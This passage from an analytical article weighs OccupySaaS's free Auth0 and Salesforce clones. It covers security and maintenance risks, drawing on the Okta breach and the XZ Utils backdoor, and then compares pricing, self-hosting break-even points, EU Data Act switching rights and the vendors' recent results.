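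The attacker took files belonging to 134 customers. Some were recordings of browser sessions that customers had sent to help Okta diagnose faults. These recordings contained session tokens, which the attacker used to take over sessions at five customers without a password. One of the five, the security company BeyondTrust, warned Okta on 2 October, but Okta didn't confirm the breach to it until 19 October. In late November, Okta added that the attacker had also downloaded the names and email addresses of everyone who used that support system. Auth0 had a separate support system, which the attacker didn't reach.

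Cloudflare, another of the five, replaced thousands of passwords and tokens that might have leaked but missed four, which an attacker used in November to get into its internal wiki and some of its source code. Okta tightened the rules for administrators' sessions and postponed product work for about 90 days to focus on security.

The attacker didn't need a flaw in Okta's login code. A bicycle shop that ran its own ZeroAuthy server would have avoided this breach, because no central support desk would have held its tokens. But BeyondTrust and Cloudflare noticed the intruder because they employ people who look for break-ins. A small shop might never find out that somebody had broken into its server.

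Okta has had flaws in its code as well. For about three months in 2024, someone could, in certain conditions, log in to an account with a username of 52 characters or more without the right password. Okta put each user's ID, username and password, in that order, into a hash function that ignores everything after 72 characters, so if the username was long enough, the function ignored the password. Okta's own staff found the mistake on 30 October and fixed it the same day for every customer.

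### What a maintained service needs besides code

If ZeroAuthy had the same flaw, its developers would have to confirm it, fix it, check which releases contained it and warn users. Each company would then be protected only after installing the fix. Attackers also read these warnings, and they can compare the old and new code to find the flaw. A company that updates its server once a month could be exposed for weeks, whereas Auth0's customers usually don't have to do anything.

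The shop's larger customers may also want an audit, in which outside specialists examine the code and try to break in. They may ask how the operator controls access to its servers and makes backups. An audit of ZeroAuthy would quickly go out of date if the code kept changing as fast as it did in October, so the developers would need to slow down or have specialists examine important changes separately.

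Maintainers would also have to keep the free versions compatible with Auth0 and Salesforce as those products change. Auth0 might release a new version of its website SDK that fixes a security hole and also starts using a new request. If the shop installs it before ZeroAuthy supports that request, its customers can't log in, but if it waits, the hole stays open. SalesCompel has a similar problem, because Salesforce releases a new API version three times a year.

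With AI agents, this part of the work could take people much less time. An agent could run the compatibility laboratory whenever Auth0 publishes an SDK, find the request that fails, write the missing code and use the SDK to check it automatically. It could also reproduce a reported flaw overnight and have a fix ready for a person to approve in the morning. A small team might then be able to keep up with security reports, as long as it knows enough to notice a mistake like the one Claude made with Cloudflare's encryption key.

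Somebody still has to be on call. If nobody can log in to the shop on the Saturday before Christmas, the cause might be ZeroAuthy, a full disk or an expired security certificate. An agent with access to the server might find out which. But if it finds signs that somebody has stolen the signing key, a person may have to decide whether to replace the key and invalidate every existing token on such a busy day. The project's volunteers can't do this for thousands of shops, so each shop would need its own technician or a company that runs ZeroAuthy for it.

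### What one anonymous maintainer can promise

Cornelißen argues that whether a login server works today matters less than who will fix its security holes in three years, pay for an audit and respond to problems at night. OccupySaaS has no convincing answer yet. The founders ask for donations, but donors can stop at any time, and a laid-off engineer who finds a new job may no longer have free evenings to work on ZeroAuthy. Hardly anyone else has contributed code, so there is no obvious successor.

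Anyone could copy the code and continue from it, but maintaining an independent version is harder. Cornelißen found more than 10,600 forks of PhotoCraft, none with a real following. The only one with a clear direction of its own removes the program's AI features and its reporting of usage data. After eight days, it had made one change and was 2,077 changes behind the original. Cornelißen therefore sees the open code as insurance in case PhotoCraft's developers stop, since a fork could then catch up and take over. The same is true of ZeroAuthy, provided someone competent wanted the job.

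An attacker might also volunteer to maintain the free versions. XZ Utils, a compression tool found on most Linux systems, depended for years on one tired volunteer. Somebody using the name Jia Tan helped him for about two years, gained permission to publish releases, and hid a back door in the program in early 2024. A Microsoft engineer found it only because he noticed remote logins taking half a second longer than usual. Attacks through shared software have since become far more common, and Passbolt has counted one nearly every other day since the start of 2026.

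A login server would be an even more attractive target than a compression tool. ZeroAuthy's users don't know who controls its main account, so they might not notice if that account passed to somebody else. The founders could reduce this risk without revealing their names, for example by requiring two people to approve each release and signing it with keys they both hold. It would help more if a foundation or a company with a known address took responsibility for the project.

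Until then, a company that wants to run its own login server would be safer with an established free one such as Keycloak or Ory Hydra, both backed by companies. The company would have to rewrite some of its login code, which ZeroAuthy is meant to make unnecessary.

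## Would customers save money, and are the vendors at risk?

Most small customers wouldn't save money by switching, because Auth0 and Salesforce charge them little or nothing and running a server costs more. A company with a few dozen people on one of Salesforce's more expensive plans might save a lot if SalesCompel were finished. Neither vendor's latest results show damage from AI-built replacements, but those results include only the first two and a half weeks after OccupySaaS published its code.

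### What Salesforce charges

The complaint about per-seat pricing fits Salesforce well. Salesforce's *Sales Pricing* lists five paid plans, which would cost the bicycle shop's five salespeople this much:

| Plan | Per user, per month | Five users, per year | Price under the plan's old name |
|---|---|---|---|
| Starter | $25 | $1,500 | |
| Pro | $100 | $6,000 | |
| Core | $195 | $11,700 | $175 (Enterprise) |
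| Advanced | $395 | $23,700 | $350 (Unlimited) |
| Max | $550 | $33,000 | $550 (Agentforce 1) |

Core costs 11% more than the plan it replaces, and Advanced costs 13% more. Salesforce had already raised Enterprise and Unlimited prices by about 6% in August 2025, according to the licensing consultancy Redress Compliance's *Enterprise Pricing Guide*. At list prices, a company that moves from Enterprise to Core therefore pays about 18% more than it did before the August increase.

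In return, Salesforce now bundles Core with a paid version of the chat service Slack, the analytics program Tableau Next and better support. That is a good deal for a company that was already buying these, but one that only wanted a CRM is paying more for products it may not use.

Connecting other software can also cost extra. Salesforce lists API access at an extra $25 per user per month on one plan, apparently Pro. The bicycle shop's website uses the API, so the shop would pay $7,500 a year for that plan with API access for five people, five times the price of Starter.

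### What Auth0 charges

Auth0 charges by monthly active users, the people who log in at least once in a month, so hiring a sixth salesperson wouldn't change the shop's bill. Auth0's *The first and last auth platform you'll ever need* lists a free plan for up to 25,000 of these users. With 3,000 customers logging in each month, the shop would probably pay nothing.

Auth0 says its cheapest paid plan, Essentials, starts at $35 a month for 500 users, and Professional starts at $240. Companies that sell to other companies need the business versions, which start at $150 and $800.

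An older Auth0 price page, *Flexible pricing for companies and developers*, lists Essentials at $23 and a free plan for 7,500 users. The starting price has since risen by half, and the free allowance has more than tripled. Auth0's *Upcoming pricing changes for the Customer Identity Cloud* announced the increase to $35 around the end of 2023.

Growth can still raise an Auth0 bill sharply. Suppose a website has 20,000 active users on the free plan and then needs to give them different roles, which is a paid feature. It must buy a plan for all 20,000, and $35 covers only the first 500. A company that upgrades also loses the free plan's one connection to a corporate customer's sign-in system unless it buys a business version.

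Start-ups can get Auth0's larger business plan free for a year, with up to 100,000 users. By the end of that year, their programmers have written a lot of code for Auth0's API, and leaving has become expensive.

For a small firm, though, Auth0's free plan currently does more than ZeroAuthy. It includes passkeys and SCIM, which ZeroAuthy lacks, and Auth0 runs the server.

### When would running a CRM be cheaper?

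A company can estimate how many salespeople it needs before its own CRM costs less than Salesforce:

```
seats needed = yearly cost of running your own system
               / yearly price per seat
```

Assume that SalesCompel already has every feature the company needs, which it doesn't. The other assumptions are also illustrative:

- Hosting and backups cost $3,000 a year.
- The system takes up a quarter of the time of a technician who costs $120,000 a year, which is $30,000.
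- Moving costs $45,000 once. Spread over three years, that is $15,000 a year.

The total is $48,000 a year. A Core seat costs $2,340 a year, and 48,000 divided by 2,340 is 20.5, so the company would save money from its 21st seat. If AI agents halved the technician's work, the total would fall to $33,000 and the company would need 15 seats. The results for all five plans are:

| Plan | Yearly price per seat | Seats needed | Seats needed if AI halves staff time |
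|---|---|---|---|
| Starter | $300 | 160 | 110 |
| Pro | $1,200 | 40 | 28 |
| Core | $2,340 | 21 | 15 |
| Advanced | $4,740 | 11 | 7 |
| Max | $6,600 | 8 | 5 |

Halving the staff time lowers the total by less than a third, because the company still has to pay for hosting and the move. AI could make the move cheaper too. Tech Times' *Salesforce Will Not Hire More Software Engineers Next Year* (2026) reports that Salesforce used Claude Code to finish a 231-day migration of its own in 13 days. If AI halved both the staff time and the cost of moving, the company would need only 11 Core seats.

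The bicycle shop would not save money by switching. The $1,500 a year it pays for Starter would cover about 25 hours of the technician's time, with nothing left for a server.

The bicycle wholesaler's savings depend on the cost of rebuilding its 20 automations. It pays Salesforce $93,600 a year for 40 people on Core, so by this estimate it would save $45,600 by leaving. But if rebuilding the automations and screens brought the cost of moving to $200,000, its own system would cost almost $100,000 a year, more than it pays Salesforce.

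Few large customers pay the list price. CostBench's *All Salesforce Plans & Pricing* cites 2,216 purchases reported to Vendr, a firm that helps companies buy software. The median customer paid $74,700 a year, and the average discount was 13%. With that discount, the company would need 24 Core seats instead of 21 to break even. The median bill would buy about 37 discounted seats, so a typical customer in this group could save money if SalesCompel were complete. But companies that get help buying software probably spend more than most.

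This calculation leaves out the staff time that Salesforce itself takes. *美国小企业掀起Salesforce“退订潮”，用AI自建软件大幅压缩成本*, 李's Chinese account of reporting by The Information, cites Bobby Mukherjee, who runs the consultancy Loka, as saying that business software usually costs four times its list price in total. If a company already had someone spending a quarter of their time on Salesforce, that person could run the new system instead. The extra cost would then be only $18,000 a year, and the price of eight Core seats would cover it.

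### The same calculation for logins

For Auth0, the calculation has to use customers instead of seats. Suppose a login server costs $3,000 a year to host and takes a tenth of the technician's time, which costs $12,000. A simple move costs $3,000, or $1,000 a year over three years. The total is $16,000 a year, more than the starting price of any self-service plan.

Auth0's starting prices work out to 7 cents per user per month on Essentials, 48 cents on Professional and $1.60 on the larger business plan. If those rates stayed the same as a company grew, running its own server would become cheaper at about 19,000 users on Essentials, 2,800 on Professional and 830 on the business plan. If AI halved the staff time, those break-even numbers would fall to about 11,900, 1,700 and 520. Auth0 may charge less per user at higher volumes, which would raise all the break-even numbers.

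The Essentials figure is below the free plan's limit of 25,000, so a company at that point could also pay nothing by moving to the free plan and giving up the paid features. Companies on the business plans could save much more, but they usually chose those plans to connect large customers' sign-in systems, which is what ZeroAuthy does worst.

### Firms that have already left Salesforce

Some small companies have reported much bigger savings than these estimates. Bratton's *How Small Firms Use Claude to Quit Salesforce* and later accounts of that report in The Information describe firms that replaced Salesforce with software they built using AI, rather than with SalesCompel.

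Hank AI, a medical software company with 24 full-time employees, stopped paying Salesforce $40,000 a year in January and expects its own program to cost about $500. Atonom, a start-up with 45 people, also gave up a $40,000 contract and expects to pay $1,200. Greenleaf Management, a property firm with about 55 employees, saves around $100,000 a year and spends about $300 a month on upkeep. EMARKETER's *Custom AI-coded apps help small firms trim SaaS expenses* reports that a Greenleaf partner told The Information the firm had been "only using a little piece" of Salesforce.

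The new costs in these accounts appear to leave out most of the staff time. The Seattle Seawolves, a rugby team, saved about $100,000 by replacing Salesforce and a ticketing system, but four of its engineers spent four months building the new app. If they worked full time and each cost as much as the technician above, the app cost $160,000, and the team would need more than a year and a half to recover that from the savings. Salesforce Ben also advises scepticism about Atonom's story, because it comes partly from Lovable, which sells the AI tool that Atonom used.

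Greenleaf's $100,000 saving is easier to believe because it includes labour. Greenleaf had employed one person full time to look after Salesforce, along with an outside consultant. It also dropped contracts with two property software companies, so not all of the saving came from leaving Salesforce.

In DevOps Paradox's *Should You Vibe Code Your Own CRM?* (2026), Eddie Cliff, Salesforce's head of small-business products, argues that the costs come later, when owners "end up spending more time vibe coding" their CRM than running the business. He has an obvious interest in saying so, but a firm whose only programmer left would soon struggle to maintain its CRM. The host, Darin Pope, suggests building one anyway, as a cheap way for a company to find out what it needs before it buys a CRM.

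Large companies move more slowly. 李 reports that the drug maker Sanofi wants AI agents to take over 80% of the work now done by ServiceNow, other software and outside contractors, saving at least $10 million a year, but that its technology staff have resisted. An executive at Engine, a travel company with about 1,000 employees, thinks leaving Salesforce would take at least a year and has no plans to try. A sales manager at the data company Databricks told The Information that customers' AI projects were replacing only parts of business programs.

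### Why free software hadn't already won

Companies could avoid these subscriptions long before OccupySaaS. Keycloak, a free login server that began at the software company Red Hat, came out in 2014, a year after Auth0's founding. SuiteCRM has offered a free CRM since 2013. Both do more than OccupySaaS's programs in most respects:

| Program | What it does | Does code written for Auth0 or Salesforce work with it? |
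|---|---|---|
| Keycloak | Complete login server, with SAML and company directories | Only where that code follows open standards |
| Ory Hydra | Issues tokens, but needs another program for accounts and the login page | Only where that code follows open standards |
| ZeroAuthy | Basic logins and most user management | Often, according to the project's tests |
| SuiteCRM | Contacts, deals, quotes and automations | No |
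| SalesCompel | Accounts and contacts | For some requests |

Customers who stayed with the paid products weighed more than the licence fee. A company that installs Keycloak still has to find someone to run it. It also has to prepare for buyers' security reviews, while Auth0 supports compliance with standards such as SOC 2 and ISO 27001 and supplies audit logs, according to Auth0's *Secure your identity in a single day*. Salesforce has about 12,000 partner firms that customers can hire, and many salespeople have used it in earlier jobs. A manager who chooses SuiteCRM to save money may get the blame if the sales team dislikes it.

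OccupySaaS's programs stand out because customers might not have to rewrite code. Suppose adapting one program's login code to Keycloak takes three days, at $500 a day. For the bicycle shop's website, that is $1,500, which wouldn't stop anyone from switching. For a company with 40 programs that use Auth0, it is $60,000, and the company has to test each program. ZeroAuthy could save the company most of that money, but the bicycle shop would gain very little from it.

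AI also makes this advantage less valuable. An agent that can imitate Auth0's API can probably rewrite a website's login code for Keycloak, which is a far smaller job. If that work took three hours instead of three days, the company with 40 programs would spend about $7,500. It might then prefer Keycloak, which has a longer record and fewer missing features.

AI tools could make CRMs easier to replace. Cliff says many companies now use Salesforce without its screens, by letting Claude or another AI tool fetch the data. Their staff would notice less if a different CRM handled those requests, so a compatible API would be worth more to them than to a company whose salespeople work in Salesforce all day.

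### What the EU Data Act requires

The EU Data Act does more than OccupySaaS to address the "export walls" the project complains about. It has applied since 12 September 2025 and covers rented software, including products that American vendors sell to customers in the EU.

A customer has to give no more than two months' notice to leave. The vendor must then normally complete the switch within 30 days, or within seven months if it shows that 30 days is technically unfeasible. The customer then has at least 30 more days to retrieve its data. The vendor must provide open interfaces for this free of charge and, where no common standard exists, export the data in a widely used format that other programs can read.

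The customer may move to another vendor or to its own servers, so a bicycle shop in Munich that left Auth0 for ZeroAuthy would have these rights. Until 12 January 2027, a vendor may charge for switching, but no more than the switch costs it. From that date it may not charge for switching, though it may still be able to claim a penalty if a customer ends a fixed-term contract early.

In the United States, customers mostly depend on their contracts. CostBench reports that Salesforce contracts usually run for at least 12 months and renew automatically unless the customer gives at least 30 days' notice.

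The Data Act helps with data much more than with software. Salesforce would have to give a European wholesaler its customer records, but wouldn't have to make the wholesaler's Apex code run anywhere else. Only for basic infrastructure, such as rented servers, must vendors help customers get comparable results after a switch. It's unclear whether Auth0 must hand over customers' password hashes.

In November 2025, the European Commission proposed relaxing the switching rules for some customised services and smaller vendors under older contracts. A company with such a contract should check whether the proposal has become law before relying on these rights.

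### The vendors' latest results

Okta and Salesforce are both still growing. 金融界's *Okta(OKTA.US)Q3电话会* (2026) reports that by 31 October, Okta's customers had signed contracts for $5.02 billion of future revenue, 17% more than a year earlier. New products made up more than 30% of bookings, and the number of customers for its AI products doubled in the quarter. Okta's chief executive, Todd McKinnon, told Alspach that customers want help deploying AI agents securely, so AI has so far created demand for Okta as well as possible competitors.

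Salesforce's revenue rose 13% to $11.63 billion in the same quarter. Xinhua's *Salesforce reports record Q3 revenue despite falling net income* (2026) attributes $470 million of this to Informatica, a company Salesforce had bought. Without Informatica, growth would have been between 8% and 9%. Salesforce expects total growth of 8–10% in the current quarter.

These results are too early to show what effect OccupySaaS has had on either company. The quarter ended 17 days after ZeroAuthy's code appeared, and most customers couldn't have left that quickly. The results are better evidence about the firms that began building their own CRMs earlier in the year. Those firms are still far too few to matter to Salesforce, which would have to lose more than 11,000 customers paying $40,000 a year each to lose 1% of its revenue.

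The share prices have moved for other reasons too. Software shares fell sharply in early 2026, when investors feared that AI agents would replace business programs, a scare nicknamed the "SaaSpocalypse". Salesforce's share price had turned upwards by the start of October, according to *〈株価反転〉SaaS終末論への反撃を始めたセールスフォース* (二階堂, 2026). Okta's share price had more than doubled during the year before its December results, according to *Okta Stock Beat, Topped $5 Billion in Backlog, and Still Dropped 8%* (Ehsan, 2026).

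Okta's shares fell 8.6% after it published its results on 1 December, which 金融界 attributes to a profit forecast below what analysts expected. Salesforce's shares fell more than 10% the next day, also after a weak forecast (Wheatley, 2026, *Salesforce's stock nosedives as soft guidance undermines a stellar quarter*). Neither report mentions free copies as a cause, though investors may be worried about AI in the long run.

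### What Salesforce says about AI replacements

Marc Benioff, Salesforce's chief executive, called the SaaSpocalypse "crazy nonsense" in September (Moore, 2026, *Salesforce CEO Marc Benioff says the SaaSpocalypse is 'crazy nonsense'*). In August he had told investors that AI models depend on CRM software and don't replace it. His best evidence was that customers were leaving at close to the lowest rate on record (Millward, 2026, *Salesforce CEO Benioff Says ‘Apps Are Not Dying’*). But a company in the second year of a three-year contract can't leave yet, so this rate may be slow to change.

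On 2 December, Benioff called the seats that customers buy "durable" and said Salesforce had lengthened every type of contract. The contract figures give this only limited support. 东方财富网's *赛富时：2027财年第三财季营收116亿美元同比增13%* (2026) puts signed future revenue at $65.3 billion, up 10%. Of that, $33.6 billion is due within a year, up 14%, so the part due later grew by only about 6%. If contracts were getting much longer, the later part should have grown faster. Benioff may be describing new contracts that haven't yet affected the total, and Informatica's contracts may also distort the comparison.

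Salesforce is also becoming less dependent on seats. Benioff told investors in August that different customers want to pay per user, per AI agent, by usage or by result, and that Salesforce now offers all four. The Core, Advanced and Max plans include credits that customers spend when AI agents work for them. This protects Salesforce if AI lets a company manage with fewer salespeople. The wholesaler might cut its team from 40 to 30 and save $23,400 on Core seats, then spend part of that on credits for the agents that took over the work. OccupySaaS's complaint about charging "by the head" would be out of date, but the wholesaler's bill would still grow with its business.

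Salesforce's partnerships with AI companies could make Salesforce either harder or easier to replace. OpenAI executives told investors earlier this year that they expected OpenAI's products to replace Salesforce's, 李 reports. Yet Salesforce has just released a plugin that lets people work with their Salesforce data inside ChatGPT, after similar ones for Claude and Microsoft's Copilot. Salesforce argues that customers' permissions and controls carry over, which gives them a reason to stay. But salespeople who work only through ChatGPT may not care which company's database it uses.

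### Using ZeroAuthy to bargain

Cornelißen, writing for the German site KIberblick, thinks ZeroAuthy's rapid development already improves customers' negotiating position, even though it can't yet replace Auth0.

Suppose the company with 40 programs pays Auth0 $30,000 a year. Running Keycloak would cost it the $16,000 a year estimated above, plus $20,000 a year for three years to rewrite its login code. The total would be $36,000 a year during that time, so Auth0 could raise its price by almost $6,000 and the company would still save money by staying. If ZeroAuthy were finished, the company could switch to it for $16,000 a year without rewriting anything. Auth0 would then have a reason to offer a discount, which the company could take without installing ZeroAuthy.

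A customer's threat to switch to ZeroAuthy works only if Auth0's salespeople believe it. They can read ZeroAuthy's list of missing features and the project's advice against using it for real accounts. If the customer needs SAML, they will know it can't leave. The threat is most believable from a company whose website has simple logins, but that company may already be on the free plan and have nothing to negotiate.

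AI seems to be helping some buyers. 李 reports that some large companies are spending more on AI while shortening their contracts with traditional software vendors or demanding better terms. Retool, which sells tools for building internal software, found that 35% of large companies had already replaced at least one rented program with one of their own, according to PYMNTS's *SMBs Swap Pricey SaaS Contracts for AI-Built Apps*. Retool benefits from that finding, but a vendor negotiating a renewal can't easily dismiss it. Each missing feature that ZeroAuthy gains would add to this pressure, at no cost to the customers who benefit.

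However, Salesforce has raised its list prices even though its customers can now build a basic CRM in weeks. Auth0 still sells paid plans, although Keycloak has been free for twelve years. SalesCompel adds little to the threat that Salesforce customers will build their own CRM, which Hank AI and Atonom have shown to be real.

A company can test Cornelißen's argument at its next renewal. If most of its programs work in a trial with ZeroAuthy and it has a technician who could run the server, it has a reasonable case for a discount. Otherwise, it should probably ask for a shorter contract so it can try again when ZeroAuthy has improved.
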